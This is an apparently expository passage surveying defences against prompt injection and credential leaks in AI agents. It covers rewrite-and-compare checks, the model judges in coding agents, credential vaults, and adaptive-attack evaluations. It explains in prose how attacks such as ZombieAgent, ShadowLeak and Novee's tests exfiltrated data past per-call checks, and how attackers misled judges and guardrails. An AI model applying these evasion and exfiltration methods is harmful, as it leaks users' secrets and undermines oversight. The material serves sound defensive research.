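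He, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *AttriGuard*, distrust such self-reports because a misled model can invent a justification. Their system makes the decision twice and compares the results. It works as follows:

1. The agent proposes a call in the normal way.
2. Another model rewrites the tool results so that they keep their facts but have less power to direct the agent. For example, it turns an order to send a report into a statement that, according to the text, someone should send it.
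3. The agent's model chooses its next step again, with the same request and the same earlier calls but the rewritten results.
4. If the second run does not use the same tool, AttriGuard blocks the original call. If both the tool and the arguments match, it allows the call. If only the tool matches, a model judge decides whether the original call still fits the user's request.

The rewriting can also turn structured data into ordinary sentences and weaken claims that an action is necessary. The original call keeps the full results, so details lost in rewriting do not affect the arguments that AttriGuard eventually sends.

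The paper defines the quantity that this comparison estimates. If p(c) is the probability that the agent makes call c, the effect of outside instructions on that call is:

```text
effect  =  log p(c | original results)  −  log p(c | results without their steering power)
```

If the probability that the agent emails the attacker is 0.9 with the original page and 0.01 with the rewritten one, the effect is about 4.5, using natural logarithms. If the probabilities for the email to the boss are 0.95 and 0.90, the effect is about 0.05. Commercial models generally do not expose these probabilities, so AttriGuard checks whether an equivalent call appears in a single second run.

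On AgentDojo, no attack from four fixed sets succeeded against any of the four models that used AttriGuard. The researchers had removed 62 of the 944 combinations of user task and attack. In some of these, the attack involved no tool call. In the others, the user had left the decision to outside text, a case that SARA's designers also exclude.

The adaptive test is more informative. The researchers selected 61 cases at random and gave an automated attacker up to 200 attempts at each, along with details of how AttriGuard worked and which calls it had blocked. The attacker succeeded against AttriGuard in 6.56 per cent of cases with Gemini 2.5 Flash and 9.84 per cent with Llama 3.3 70B. It succeeded in 29.51 and 40.98 per cent of cases against PromptArmor, a defence that removes injected text from tool results and had stopped every fixed attack on these cases.

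These rates amount to four and six successes in 61 cases, so the true rates could plausibly be roughly 2 to 16 per cent and 4 to 20 per cent. Raising the limit to 500 attempts produced no further successes with Gemini. The adaptive test used a stronger form of rewriting than the main tests. In a smaller comparison on GPT-4.1-mini, that form reduced benign utility from 70.59 to 67.65 per cent.

AttriGuard increased the average time per task from 11.5 to 32.4 seconds with Gemini and from 14.2 to 41.2 seconds with Llama. CaMeL took 165.5 and 105.4 seconds on the same models. With Llama, the agent also processed about twice as many input tokens as without a defence. These figures come from runs under attack, so they may differ for ordinary work.

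The comparison can detect outside control of the agent, but it may miss an accidental leak. If an agent includes an API key in an email by mistake, the second run may repeat the mistake and make the call look legitimate.

### Judges in Claude Code and Codex

Model judges are now part of widely used coding agents. In Claude Code's auto mode, file reads and edits within the project skip the judge, while shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools normally go to it. The judge first answers only yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags a call, it considers the same material again with written reasoning. Anthropic reports these error rates:

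| Stage | Harmless calls blocked (10,000 real calls) | Overeager actions missed (52 real cases) | Data theft missed (1,000 artificial cases) |
|---|---|---|---|
| First answer only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most false alarms but lets more dangerous calls through. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the judge correctly identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having agreed to it. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" has not necessarily agreed to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic could not find wording for the prompt that solved this without creating worse problems.

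Anthropic later hired Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, to attack the judge. After Anthropic gave the judge more information, such as whether a repository is public, its miss rate on Apollo's attacks fell from 12 to 7 per cent. Anthropic also added a category of actions that the judge should never approve, such as sending secrets to outside services. A user who wants such an action has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves.

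OpenAI's judge for Codex, released in April 2026, reviews only actions that would leave the agent's sandbox. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from OpenAI's own use in which 720 of 10,000 actions went to the judge. It refused seven, and after four of those refusals the agent found a safer way to continue.

In artificial tests, OpenAI's judge refused 90.3 per cent of overeager actions and 99.3 per cent of prompt-injected attempts to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data. The second figure drops to 90.2 per cent when the test also includes deleting and altering data, although Trębacz and colleagues consider many of the additional misses too minor to block. They report that human and automated testers found ways to mislead the judge into approving commands, and they do not expect this kind of system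 to provide guarantees.

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to compare the two products. In July 2026, Trajectory Labs ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attacks succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. But attacks on these models succeeded only 0.09 per cent of the time on average even when nothing checked their calls, so the result is weak evidence of how well the judge works. The test was more informative for Codex, where attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded in 19.03 per cent of attempts with full access and 5.83 per cent with Auto-review. OpenAI has since updated Auto-review, and the test did not include either company's browser safeguards.

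Neither company says how long the check delays each call. Anthropic says its judge uses a small number of extra tokens per call, and in August it stopped charging Claude Code users on its individual and Team plans for those tokens.

### The four example calls

The following table gives the verdicts a competent judge should reach, first from the call alone and then from the call and the user's request together. A real judge may not always reach them.

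| Call | Call alone | Call and request |
|---|---|---|
| A: summary to the boss | Probably allow, since it looks like ordinary work | Allow, because the user asked for this email |
| B: report to the attacker | Uncertain, since companies do send reports to outsiders | Block, because the user asked for something else |
| C: summary and API key to the boss | Block, because a summary has no need for a key | Block, because the request does not call for the key |
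| D: token to the code host | Probably allow, since tokens normally go in this header | Allow, because the user asked for the list of issues |

The verdict on B depends most on knowing what the user asked for. If the user had asked the agent to send the quarterly report to that address, the same call would be correct. The user's request also confirms that A and D are part of the task.

C is different because a judge can recognise the problem from general knowledge about keys. It may even detect a key in Base64, since a long meaningless string does not belong in a web page summary. The request in D includes the reason for contacting the code host but not the name of the company that issued the token, so the judge has to infer the issuer from the prefix and the address or get it from a list.

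To check C and D, the judge has to read an argument that contains a secret. If the judge runs on a different company's servers from the agent's model, each check gives that company a copy of the credential. Bhagwatkar and colleagues mention a similar risk for their firewalls. The harness could replace the secret with a label such as "API key" before it sends the argument to the judge. The judge could still flag C, but it could no longer check that the token in D was the right one.

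## Keeping credentials out of the model's reach

Scanners and judges look for a secret after the model has received it. Another approach is to never give the model the secret. The model names a connection, and a trusted program outside the agent adds the credential once a check has approved the call. This program is called a vault, broker or proxy, depending on the product.

### Call D without a token

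In the original call D, the model wrote the code host's token into a request header. With a vault, it writes only this:

```text
D  http_request(
     connection = "codehost",
     url        = "https://api.codehost.example/issues")
```

The call then goes through five steps:

1. The harness runs its usual check, such as the permission rule that allows this web address.
2. If the check approves the call, the harness passes it to the vault.
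3. The vault looks up its record for "codehost". The record contains the token, the host it belongs to, and the part of the request where that host expects it.
4. The vault compares the host in the web address with the host in the record. If they match, it adds the header "Authorization: Bearer ghp_...". If they differ, the request gets no token.
5. The vault sends the request and returns the list of issues to the agent, without the header.

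Kenney and colleagues describe a vault of this kind, Corvic Security Vault, in which each record is a "connector" and the agent's code receives only a list of connector names. Step 4, host binding, prevents the leak of the token to the code host's public status page described earlier, because that page is on a different host. *CapSeal* (2026), a similar design, also restricts the path within a host and the number of requests.

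In *aiAuthZ* (2026), the agent instead writes a placeholder where the secret would go, and a gateway replaces the placeholder with the real secret after authorising the call. The check runs on the call with the placeholder still in it, so a model judge on another company's servers could review call D without receiving the secret.

*Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a security design for healthcare that keeps credentials in a separate container beside each agent. An audit had found keys in start-up scripts, `.env` files and configuration files that any user of the machine could read. An attacker who takes over the agent can still send requests through the container, within its limits on destination, size and frequency, but cannot extract the keys to use elsewhere.

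All this works only if the agent cannot read the vault's files or memory. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) therefore requires its credential program to run outside the agent's user account or sandbox. *CapSeal* assumes the attacker does not fully control the operating system.

### What happens to call C

The key in call C came from a configuration file. If the company moves the key to a vault, the file might contain only a name:

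```text
API_KEY = {{reports_key}}
```

The agent can still copy this line into its email, but the boss then receives a name that is useless without access to the vault. This protection works regardless of what caused the mistake. Encoding or splitting the text can defeat a scanner, but it would not give an attacker the credential here.

Placeholders create a new danger, because a gateway that replaced them anywhere in an approved call would put the real key into the body of the email. Authorisation alone would not prevent this, since the recipient rule approves call C. The gateway has to replace each placeholder only in the right field of a request to the right host. Having the model just name a connection avoids the problem, because the model never marks a place for the secret.

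The company also has to change every program that reads the key from the file. If one still needs the file, the usable key stays on disk, where the agent can find it.

The vault does not stop Call B, which emails the internal report to the attacker. The call contains no credential, and the vault would supply the mail account's credential to send it.

### Sixteen probes of one vault

Kenney and colleagues tested Corvic Security Vault, their own company's product, on September 27, 2026. They ran two experiments in the product's sandbox, one with only a GitHub connector and the other with only a connector for FRED, an economic data service of the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis. They wrote down the expected result of each probe beforehand.

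| What the code in the sandbox tried | Result |
|---|---|
| Request GitHub account details without supplying a credential | Succeeded, so the vault had added one |
| Search its environment variables | 20 variables, no secret found |
| Look in 12 common locations for credential files | None of the files existed |
| Examine its own GitHub request before sending it | No authorization header |
| Contact three services that repeat back what they receive | No token came back |
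| Ask OpenAI's service for a list of models | Refused, because the request had no credential |
| Contact the internal addresses where cloud machines obtain credentials | No answer within six seconds |

All 16 probes had the expected security outcome. The result depends on the successful GitHub request, because a sandbox with no network connection would also have passed every leak test.

The FRED connector did not work. Its record set the vault to put the key in an authorization header, but FRED requires the key in the web address, as a parameter called "api_key". FRED returned an error because the parameter was missing. The researchers scored whether a connector worked separately from whether it was secure, so this failure does not count against the 16.

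The FRED experiment is weaker evidence because no request with the FRED key ever succeeded. Nothing confirms that the vault was attaching the key to any request, so the key's absence from requests to other hosts means little. Correcting the record would put the key in a web address, which servers are likely to log. Kenney and colleagues recommend removing such secrets from logs.

They did not test several ways around host binding. A permitted host can redirect a request to another address, and a program that follows the redirect with the header still attached gives the token to the new host. In DNS rebinding, an attacker changes which machine a host name leads to. The researchers also left out:

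- a permitted host under an attacker's control
- theft of a token while the vault renews it
- session data in MCP
- tools that operate a web browser

They also did not verify how the vault encrypts its secrets, separates one customer from another, controls its administrators' access, or replaces old credentials. These protections matter because a vault holds many credentials in one place. Kenney and colleagues cite a disclosure by the AI platform Hugging Face, which detected unauthorised access to its users' stored secrets in 2024 and advised them to replace their credentials.

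The experiments included no prompt injection either. The researchers consider running an established injection benchmark against the vault the most valuable next step.

### Whether a vault replaces scanning

If no secret ever enters the model's context, the model cannot copy one into a tool argument, so a company could switch off its argument scanner and avoid the false alarms. This reasoning is largely sound for the credentials in the vault, provided that no service sends them back in a response.

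But agents also receive credentials that nobody has put in a vault. The OpenID Foundation (2026), which develops standards for online identity, told the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) that the most pressing threat to agents is people sharing their own credentials with them, including passwords, API keys and session cookies. An agent can also ask its user for more information during a task, through an MCP feature called elicitation. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a post on agents' credentials, warns that such a request might be for a password, although MCP's documentation advises against asking for one.

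Old project files may contain forgotten keys, and error messages may print keys. Some tools return new secrets in normal use, for example when a user asks an agent to create an API key. These secrets all reach the model without passing through the vault.

A tool may also bypass the vault. *aiAuthZ* governs only the tools connected to its gateway, so an agent's built-in shell could still read a `.env` file. The paper proposes three countermeasures, from weakest to strongest. A program can warn when built-in tools overlap with the gateway's, an isolated network can make the gateway the only way out, and the company can store secrets only on the gateway, which leaves no long-lived credential on the agent's machine for a tool outside the gateway to read.

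Kenney and colleagues promote a vault but still recommend scanning chat messages, prompts, tool descriptions and logs for credentials. When a user pastes a key, the system should block the message and offer to set up a connector instead. This works better than waiting for the key to appear in a tool argument, because the key never reaches the model.

A vault also makes scanning more accurate. The scanner described earlier needed an exception for call D. If the vault adds the token after the scan, that exception is no longer needed, and the scanner can treat any credential in an argument as a probable mistake.

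### Misusing access without the secret

An agent can still misuse a token that it never receives, for example by deleting files through the vault on an injected instruction.

Kenney and colleagues acknowledge this in their ratings of eight threats. They scored likelihood and impact from 1 to 5 and multiplied the two, first without a vault and then with one:

| Threat | Without a vault | With a vault |
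|---|---|---|
| Connector with too much access | 20 | 15 |
| Indirect prompt injection | 25 | 12 |
| Reuse of a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Leak through logs or errors | 16 | 8 |
| Misconfigured connector | 9 | 6 |
| Secret pasted into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Credential sent to the wrong host | 20 | 4 |
| Credential found in the agent's environment | 20 | 4 |

Excessive access and indirect injection remain the two largest risks. The paper also describes them as the threats that changed least, but in its scores injection fell by 13 points and misconfiguration by only 3.

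The vault's own developers based these scores on expert judgement, not measurement. The score of 4 for pasted secrets seems especially optimistic because it assumes people will use the vault. The OpenID Foundation's account suggests many will keep pasting passwords unless using the vault is just as easy.

### Limiting what a token can do

Companies can reduce the remaining risk by giving the vault weaker tokens. A token can be limited in scope (the operations it permits), audience (the services that accept it), and lifetime. For call D, the token needs only permission to read the issues of one project on the code host, and it could expire after an hour. Anyone who stole it could then read those issues until it expired. A general token might let the thief change every project the user has, for as long as it stayed valid.

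A token's lifetime has to be short to make much difference. In the Dragos experiment described earlier, attackers tried some of the stolen keys within hours, so they could still have used a token that was valid for a day. In the cloud version of *Agent Authenticator*, a credential lasts for one task.

Another protection, Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP), ties a token to its owner by requiring the program that sends the token to prove with each request that it has a particular private key. A copied token is useless by itself, unlike the bearer tokens described in the first section. NIST recommends this method against many kinds of token theft. DPoP does not help when an attacker acts through the agent, because the program that sends the agent's requests has the private key.

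Not every service offers such tokens. MCP adopted the authorisation standard OAuth 2.1 in March 2025, which can provide short-lived tokens with a limited scope. But Trail of Bits' *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP* (2025) pointed out a month later that many of the services behind MCP tools did not support OAuth and still required API keys. According to NIST, API keys give broad access to a service with no finer control. A broker can limit that access by forwarding only certain requests, as *CapSeal* does, but this works only if nobody obtains the key.

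Choosing the right scope is also difficult. In the draft NIST paper *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) ask how to give an agent the least access it needs when nobody can fully predict its actions. Even a well-chosen scope may be too coarse to distinguish between the example calls. Permission to send email normally covers every recipient, so it would allow both call A and call B.

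### What official bodies recommend

OWASP, a non-profit foundation that publishes widely used lists of software security risks, has one list for MCP and another for agents. The MCP list, still in beta, puts "Token Mismanagement & Secret Exposure" first. This entry covers credentials written into code, long-lived tokens, and secrets that remain in a model's memory or in logs. The second entry is scope creep, in which temporary or loosely defined permissions grow over time.

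OWASP (2025) published its list for agents in December, with contributions from more than 100 experts and practitioners. It covers similar topics. Descope, which sells identity software, quotes the list's advice to "issue short-lived, narrowly scoped tokens per task".

In *Back to the Future*, NIST recommends giving each agent its own identity and credentials, linked to the person or system that operates it. If an agent logs in with a user's password, the records cannot show whether the user or the agent acted. NIST also warns of approval fatigue. It concedes that standards for consumer agents are at an early stage, and that people will keep sharing passwords unless the secure method is also easy.

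The Australian Signals Directorate (2026), a government cyber security agency, and its international partners advise organisations to introduce agents gradually, limit them to low-risk tasks, and strictly control what they can access.

NIST has not yet turned its advice into a full guideline. Its cybersecurity centre, the NCCoE, has published a summary of the comments on the draft paper. The project's page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization* (it uses "SI" for "super intelligence"), still lists the work as open for comments.

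## How inspection holds up against attacks it was not built for

A vault does not stop call B, the email that sends an internal report to an attacker. To stop calls like this one, a company has to rely on inspection, and the case for inspection depends on four premises:

1. Every harmful call passes the check before it runs.
2. The harm is visible in the call.
3. The check recognises the harm even in a new form.
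4. False alarms are few enough for people to keep the check on.

Scripts that make their own network requests bypass the check, and even a low false-alarm rate can overwhelm a reviewer with false alarms when attacks are rare. Designers can measure both problems in advance, but it is harder to measure whether the harm will be visible and recognisable, because that depends on what attackers think of next.

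### New wording, new channels and new goals

An attack can differ from those a check was designed for in its wording, channel or goal. The attacker may seek the same action with a differently phrased injection or argument, get data out by a route the designers did not treat as an exit, or want something that no rule forbids, such as a biased summary.

New wording mainly defeats checks that look for suspicious text, such as the patterns that missed most of the subtler injections in Munirathinam's test. A rule that permits only the boss's address blocks call B no matter how the instruction on the web page is worded.

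Rules have a similar weakness, because the same argument can often be written in more than one way. Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar (2026), in *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component*, tested four rule checkers on 33 variants of harmful calls. The checker that examined only the tool's name admitted 27 of them. Simple checks on the arguments admitted 18, and more careful ones admitted six. The strictest checker, which permitted only the actions that the current task needed and limited where confidential data could go, admitted one.

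Checks that cover only certain channels fail when an attack sends data out through another one. For example, a rule that stops the email tool from sending secrets does not stop an agent from putting them in a search query. Rules that block every call they do not explicitly allow work better, unless an allowed call can also carry the data out.

Attacks with a new goal are the hardest to stop. ClawGuard let some of these through because they required no forbidden tool. Provenance labels do not help if the policy allows an email's body to come from any source, as PACT does. A model judge has a better chance of catching these attacks because it compares the tool call with the user's request, but it may not be able to tell a false claim in a summary from a true one.

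| Check | New wording | New channel | New goal |
|---|---|---|---|
| Content scanner | Often fails | Fails if no single argument contains a recognisable secret | Fails, because there is no secret or attack pattern to find |
| Permission rules | Hold if they cover every way of writing the argument | Hold if they block the channel by default | Fail if the action is permitted |
| Provenance labels | Hold if the labels are correct | Fail if the labels do not cover the channel | Fail if the harm is in content that may come from outside |
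| Model judge | May fail, because the judge also interprets text | May fail if it reviews each call alone | Can succeed if the request clearly rules out the action |

### ZombieAgent: a leak across permitted requests

ZombieAgent, an attack on ChatGPT, used a new channel. Zvika Babo of the security company Radware found it and reported it to OpenAI in September 2025. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, OpenAI fixed the problem in mid-December, and Babo published his findings on January 8, 2026.

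The attack followed ShadowLeak, an earlier attack from Radware in which a single email led ChatGPT's research agent to add private data from a user's inbox to a web address and open that address. Website operators can read the addresses that visitors request, so the attacker received the data. OpenAI responded with a rule on the argument that allowed ChatGPT to open an address only exactly as supplied.

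ZombieAgent leaked private data without breaking the rule against altering addresses. ChatGPT opened a series of addresses unchanged, and the series as a whole contained the data. A check that examined each request separately would have found nothing wrong. Radware points out that a company's existing security controls would have had great difficulty detecting the attack, because the user had only asked for help with Gmail and the requests left from OpenAI's servers.

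Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, measured a similar effect in 480 runs with a small open model. Splitting a secret across several requests cut the amount revealed in any single request by 73 per cent and got past simple filters for sensitive data. Network controls, such as a list of permitted sites, worked considerably better than defences in the model's prompt.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a different rule for web addresses, under which ChatGPT may open an address automatically only if that exact address is already in an independent index of the public web. A crawler builds the index without access to anyone's conversations, so an address in it is unlikely to contain a particular user's data. If the address is not in the index, the agent tries another site or the user sees a warning.

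OpenAI considered a list of trusted sites insufficient because a trusted site can redirect a visitor elsewhere. A strict list would also produce so many warnings that users might learn to click through them. OpenAI's post does not mention ZombieAgent or give the date the new rule took effect.

The older rule prohibited one method, adding text to an address. The newer one targets the harm more directly by checking whether the address could contain private data. Rules like this should keep working against more new methods of attack. OpenAI claims only that the newer rule prevents quiet leaks through addresses, not that the pages are safe to read. Its wider system, Safe Url, checks for information from the conversation that is about to go to a third party. OpenAI says the system then either blocks the transfer or shows the user the information and asks the user to confirm.

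Another response is to keep a record of the whole session. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) gives the example of an agent that reads a confidential quarterly document, summarises it, drafts a message and sends it to an outside recipient. The user has permission for every step, so checking each step separately allows the leak. In the paper's design, the agent has lost permission to send anything outside by the last step.

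A rule written for the task, like the one that blocked call B, would stop the email in this example by checking only its recipient. Session records are more useful where a company has only general rules or an agent has to contact many outsiders. But they can also block legitimate work, such as sending a customer a quotation after reading an internal price list.

### Novee's tests: safe decisions that combine into a leak

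The harm in ZombieAgent was spread over several calls, while in tests by Elad Meged, a founding engineer at Novee Security, it came from what happened to a call's result. Meged tested Claude Code, Google's Gemini CLI and OpenAI's Codex in the vendors' own GitHub repositories, where the agents process bug reports and proposed changes automatically, without anyone approving each step. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* reported the results in July 2026.

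In Anthropic's workflow, text from an outsider led the agent to propose a command. The harness approved the command because it appeared safe, and a later stage published the output by default. As Meged put it, "Neither decision is wrong alone," but together they exposed secrets. A check on the command's arguments could not have detected the leak reliably, because the arguments did not show that the output would become public.

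Anthropic fixed each problem that Meged reported and paid him a reward for each one. But he also learned from each fix where the boundary between safe and unsafe now lay, and so where to look next. By the final round he was recovering secrets through a channel that had survived every earlier fix and needed no connection to an attacker's server. Each fix closed the specific hole, so he does not blame careless repairs. He argues that paying for individual faults encourages a vendor to treat each one as finished when the underlying weakness remains.

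The other two products had related weaknesses. Gemini CLI did not enforce one of the operator's restrictions when a command ran. In Codex, information written by one stage of a workflow could become trusted input for the next. eSecurity Planet's *Critical Flaws Found in Anthropic, Google, and OpenAI Coding Agents* adds that the Anthropic fault let attackers steal GitHub and Anthropic credentials, and that Anthropic issued several patches before giving the fault a public vulnerability number. Google rated its fault 10.0, the highest possible severity, and changed how Gemini CLI decides what to trust when it runs unattended.

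Novee has a commercial interest in such findings because it builds agents for security testing, but the vendors' patches, rewards and severity rating support Meged's account. Three companies made similar mistakes, which suggests a shared design assumption that once one component has judged something safe, later components can rely on that judgement.

Meged recommends checking a result again wherever another component uses it. The harness would inspect a command's output before publishing it, even if the command itself had passed inspection. This would address the weakness more directly than another rule about commands, but developers would have to find every point where one stage passes data to another, and missing one would leave the same kind of gap. Keeping keys in a vault off the machine would limit the damage, because a command could not print them.

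### Persistent attackers: a comparison of defences

Aljumaily and colleagues published a comparison in November 2026 that includes attackers who can try again after a failed attempt. The study used a simulated agent with 12 tools and 13 tasks, some of which involved industrial equipment. A separate program determined whether each attack had caused an action that the user's request did not authorise.

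The researchers also rated the harm from 0 to 10, based on the worst action that took place. Writing a file scored 3, sending an email 5, deleting a file 7, changing a configuration 9, and sending out confidential data 10.

The table compares a single attack with a campaign of up to 25 attempts, in which the attacker also varied the arguments. The guardrails in the second row mark outside text as data and use a language model to detect injections. "Task rules" is the strictest of the four rule checkers described above. Under "Approval and tracking", a person reviews the most dangerous calls and, once the agent has read untrusted text, nearly every call that changes something.

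| Defence | Success in one attempt | Success within 25 attempts | Average harm within 25 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 62.8% | 100% | 6.69 |
| Guardrails | 6.6% | 100% | 6.69 |
| Task rules | 4% | 8% | 0.23 |
| Task rules, approval and tracking | 1% | 3% | 0.09 |
| Approval and tracking without rules | 18% | 64% | 4.47 |

On a single attempt, the guardrails look almost as good as the task rules. After 25 attempts they offer no protection. Part of this is simple probability. If each attempt had the same independent 6.6 per cent chance, the attacker would succeed at least once in about 82 per cent of campaigns:

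```text
1 − (1 − 0.066)²⁵ ≈ 0.82
```

The remaining rise to 100 per cent comes from the simulation's assumptions that attacks grow stronger with each attempt and that guardrails weaken. In another simulation by the same researchers, where guardrails did not weaken, persistent attackers succeeded only about 22 to 45 per cent of the time against marking, with or without a detector.

Repetition is much less effective against the task rules because it does not add to the actions they permit. Even when the researchers assumed that the attacker fully controlled the model, average harm with task rules was 0.69, and no action rated 8 or higher took place.

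This result also depends on favourable conditions. The rules permitted exactly the actions that the scoring program counted as authorised, so their success is partly built into the test. Real rules have gaps, and when the researchers included each rule with a probability of 80 per cent, average harm under a fully controlled model rose from 0.69 to 1.62. At 60 per cent it was 3.21.

The benefit of human approval is even less certain. The simulated reviewer catches 90 per cent of harmful calls at first and becomes less reliable as requests accumulate, but the human testers in Anthropic's experiment caught far fewer.

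Approval and tracking without rules failed completely against a fully controlled model, even with the more attentive simulated reviewer, because the model could keep requesting approval until the reviewer made a mistake. Automatically refusing all requests after the first reduced the share of episodes with a severe action from 100 to 17.3 per cent. A company that uses human approval should therefore limit how often an agent can request it.

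The attacks that got past the task rules used permitted actions with harmful content, such as a false statement in a report the user requested. Aljumaily and colleagues conclude that more argument checking cannot stop these attacks, which are another instance of the new-goal problem. Human review of the content helped mainly in these cases.

### The same comparison with real models

The researchers then ran the 13 tasks on two small open models, Qwen2.5-1.5B and Qwen2.5-7B, testing each defence against 156 attacks per model. They did not test human approval or provenance tracking this way, so the evidence for those two comes only from the simulation. The next table shows how often the attacker achieved their goal.

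| Defence | Qwen2.5-1.5B | Qwen2.5-7B |
|---|---|---|
| None | 66% | 86% |
| Security instructions in the prompt | 65% | 55% |
| Marking outside text, with a detector | 10% | 0% |
| Simple argument checks | 10% | 21% |
| Careful argument checks | 9% | 22% |
| Task rules | 1% | 8% |

On the larger model, the guardrails in the third row did better than the task rules. The researchers calculated that an attacker who made ten attempts with the most effective type of attack would succeed against these guardrails in 38 per cent of cases on the smaller model and in none on the larger. This contradicts the simulation's result that every combination of guardrails eventually fails. The results for security instructions alone fit the simulation better, with calculated attack success rates of 91 and 85 per cent after ten attempts.

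However, the calculation cannot show whether guardrails weaken as an attacker learns from failures, because it combines the results of separate attempts and assumes they are independent. The attacks were also fixed in advance. The 100 per cent figure is therefore unconfirmed, but the zero is not evidence of safety against someone who studies the detector.

An earlier test on the smaller model cast doubt on another of the simulation's assumptions, that attacks are weaker or stronger versions of one another. One type of attack succeeded in half of its attempts, while another that the researchers had ranked as stronger succeeded in only 4 per cent.

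The task rules behaved more predictably. Every attack that passed them, on either model, involved the same task, in which the attacker wanted a false statement in a permitted report. How often these attacks succeeded depended on the model. On the larger model, 12 succeeded, which would be every attack on that task if the 156 attacks were spread evenly over the 13 tasks.

### Why fixed test sets flatter defences

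Most of the results described so far come from testing a check on attacks that existed before it did. A designer can read those attacks, and a check can do well by recognising features they happen to share. Bhagwatkar and colleagues, who created the Minimizer and Sanitizer, found that many benchmark attacks use rigid formats and ignore the surrounding task.

To see how much this matters, they attacked two filters in three stages on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. Each later stage used only the cases where the previous attacks had failed. The first stage used AgentDojo's own attacks, and the second used seven new templates that relied on deception instead of obvious instructions. In the third, a language model with information about the defence revised its attacks over ten rounds.

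| Stage | Added successes against PromptArmor | Added successes against the Sanitizer |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo's attacks | 8.0% | 0.0% |
| New templates | 64.0% | 12.5% |
| Attacker that adapts | 3.5% | 17.5% |
| Total | 75.5% | 30.0% |

Most of PromptArmor's failures came from the new wording in the templates, before the attacker had adapted to the defence. The Sanitizer resisted the templates better, and more than half of its failures required an attacker that learned from the defence. Bhagwatkar and colleagues attribute this to the Sanitizer rewriting each tool result instead of searching for suspicious passages to delete. They were testing their own design against someone else's, though. Both defences filter what the agent reads, so the experiment does not measure how well the Minimizer or any other check on arguments would hold up.

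The same pattern appears in other defences. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) bypassed 12 published defences in *The Attacker Moves Second*. Their attacks had a success rate above 90 per cent against most of them, although the original evaluations of the majority had found rates near zero.

Tests that use only fixed attacks can also fail to show which of two checks is better. In Aljumaily and colleagues' simulation, a simple argument check and a careful one each let through 15 per cent of single attacks by an attacker who did not vary the arguments. Against the persistent attacker who did vary them, the rates were 84.6 per cent for the simple check and 30.8 per cent for the careful one. The two checks also tied in the tests on real models, because those attacks did not vary the arguments either.

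Benchmarks have other faults, not all of which favour defences. ASB, one of the two benchmarks used to test Progent, adds the attacker's tools to those the agent has selected and counts any use of them as a successful attack. When Bhagwatkar and colleagues let GPT-4o choose its own tools, the attack success rate without a defence fell from 73.58 to 9.25 per cent. The original setting makes an undefended agent look far more vulnerable than it is, so a defence can appear more effective. This may have contributed to Progent's large improvement on ASB. ASB's tools also take no arguments, so the benchmark cannot test a check on arguments.

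InjecAgent, another benchmark, does not measure whether the agent completes its tasks. A check that blocked every call would get a perfect score.

Parts of AgentDojo make agents look less useful under attack than they are. Some injections overwrite information that the task needs, such as the amounts on a bill, so the agent fails even if it ignores the attacker. Some scoring is also too strict. One task asks the agent to send a person a summary, and the agent is marked as having failed if that person receives any other message. After researchers corrected such faults, the share of tasks that an undefended GPT-4o completed under attack rose from 60.87 to 72.19 per cent.

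### An adaptive test of permission rules

Few researchers have tested checks on tool calls against attackers who adapt. When He and colleagues tested AttriGuard this way, the attacker succeeded in up to about 10 per cent of cases. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports a smaller test of Progent, with Qwen2.5-7B as both the agent and the model that writes Progent's rules.

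The attack targeted the model that writes the rules, because persuasive text has no effect on the program that applies them. The injected text presented the harmful action as an approved part of the task, so that the model might widen the rules to allow it. The table gives averages over three runs on AgentDojo's banking, Slack and office tasks.

| | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
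|---|---|---|---|
| Attack success | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| User tasks completed under attack | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

The adaptive attack did worse than the standard one, probably because the milder wording intended for the rule-writing model was also less effective at steering the agent. The low success rate may therefore reflect a weak attack as much as a strong defence. On banking tasks alone, the success rate rose from 1.9 to 3.7 per cent, but with about 72 cases per run, that is roughly one more successful attack. The office tasks provided no evidence either way, because no attack on them succeeded even without a defence.

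With Progent's protection, the agent completed far fewer tasks here, and each task required about 15 times as many model calls. Both figures might improve with a stronger model. Narisetty and colleagues describe their results as preliminary and have not had them peer reviewed. They work for LaunchSafe, which builds its security products on this kind of rule enforcement.

They also list weaknesses that would remain even if no adaptive attack could break the rules. Some tasks, like the invoice payment described earlier, require outside text to determine an action. Information can also leak through a program's behaviour rather than through an argument, and CaMeL's designers demonstrated two such leaks in their own system. An attacker might also cause harm using only permitted actions. Narisetty and colleagues did not test this kind of attack, but name it as their next experiment.
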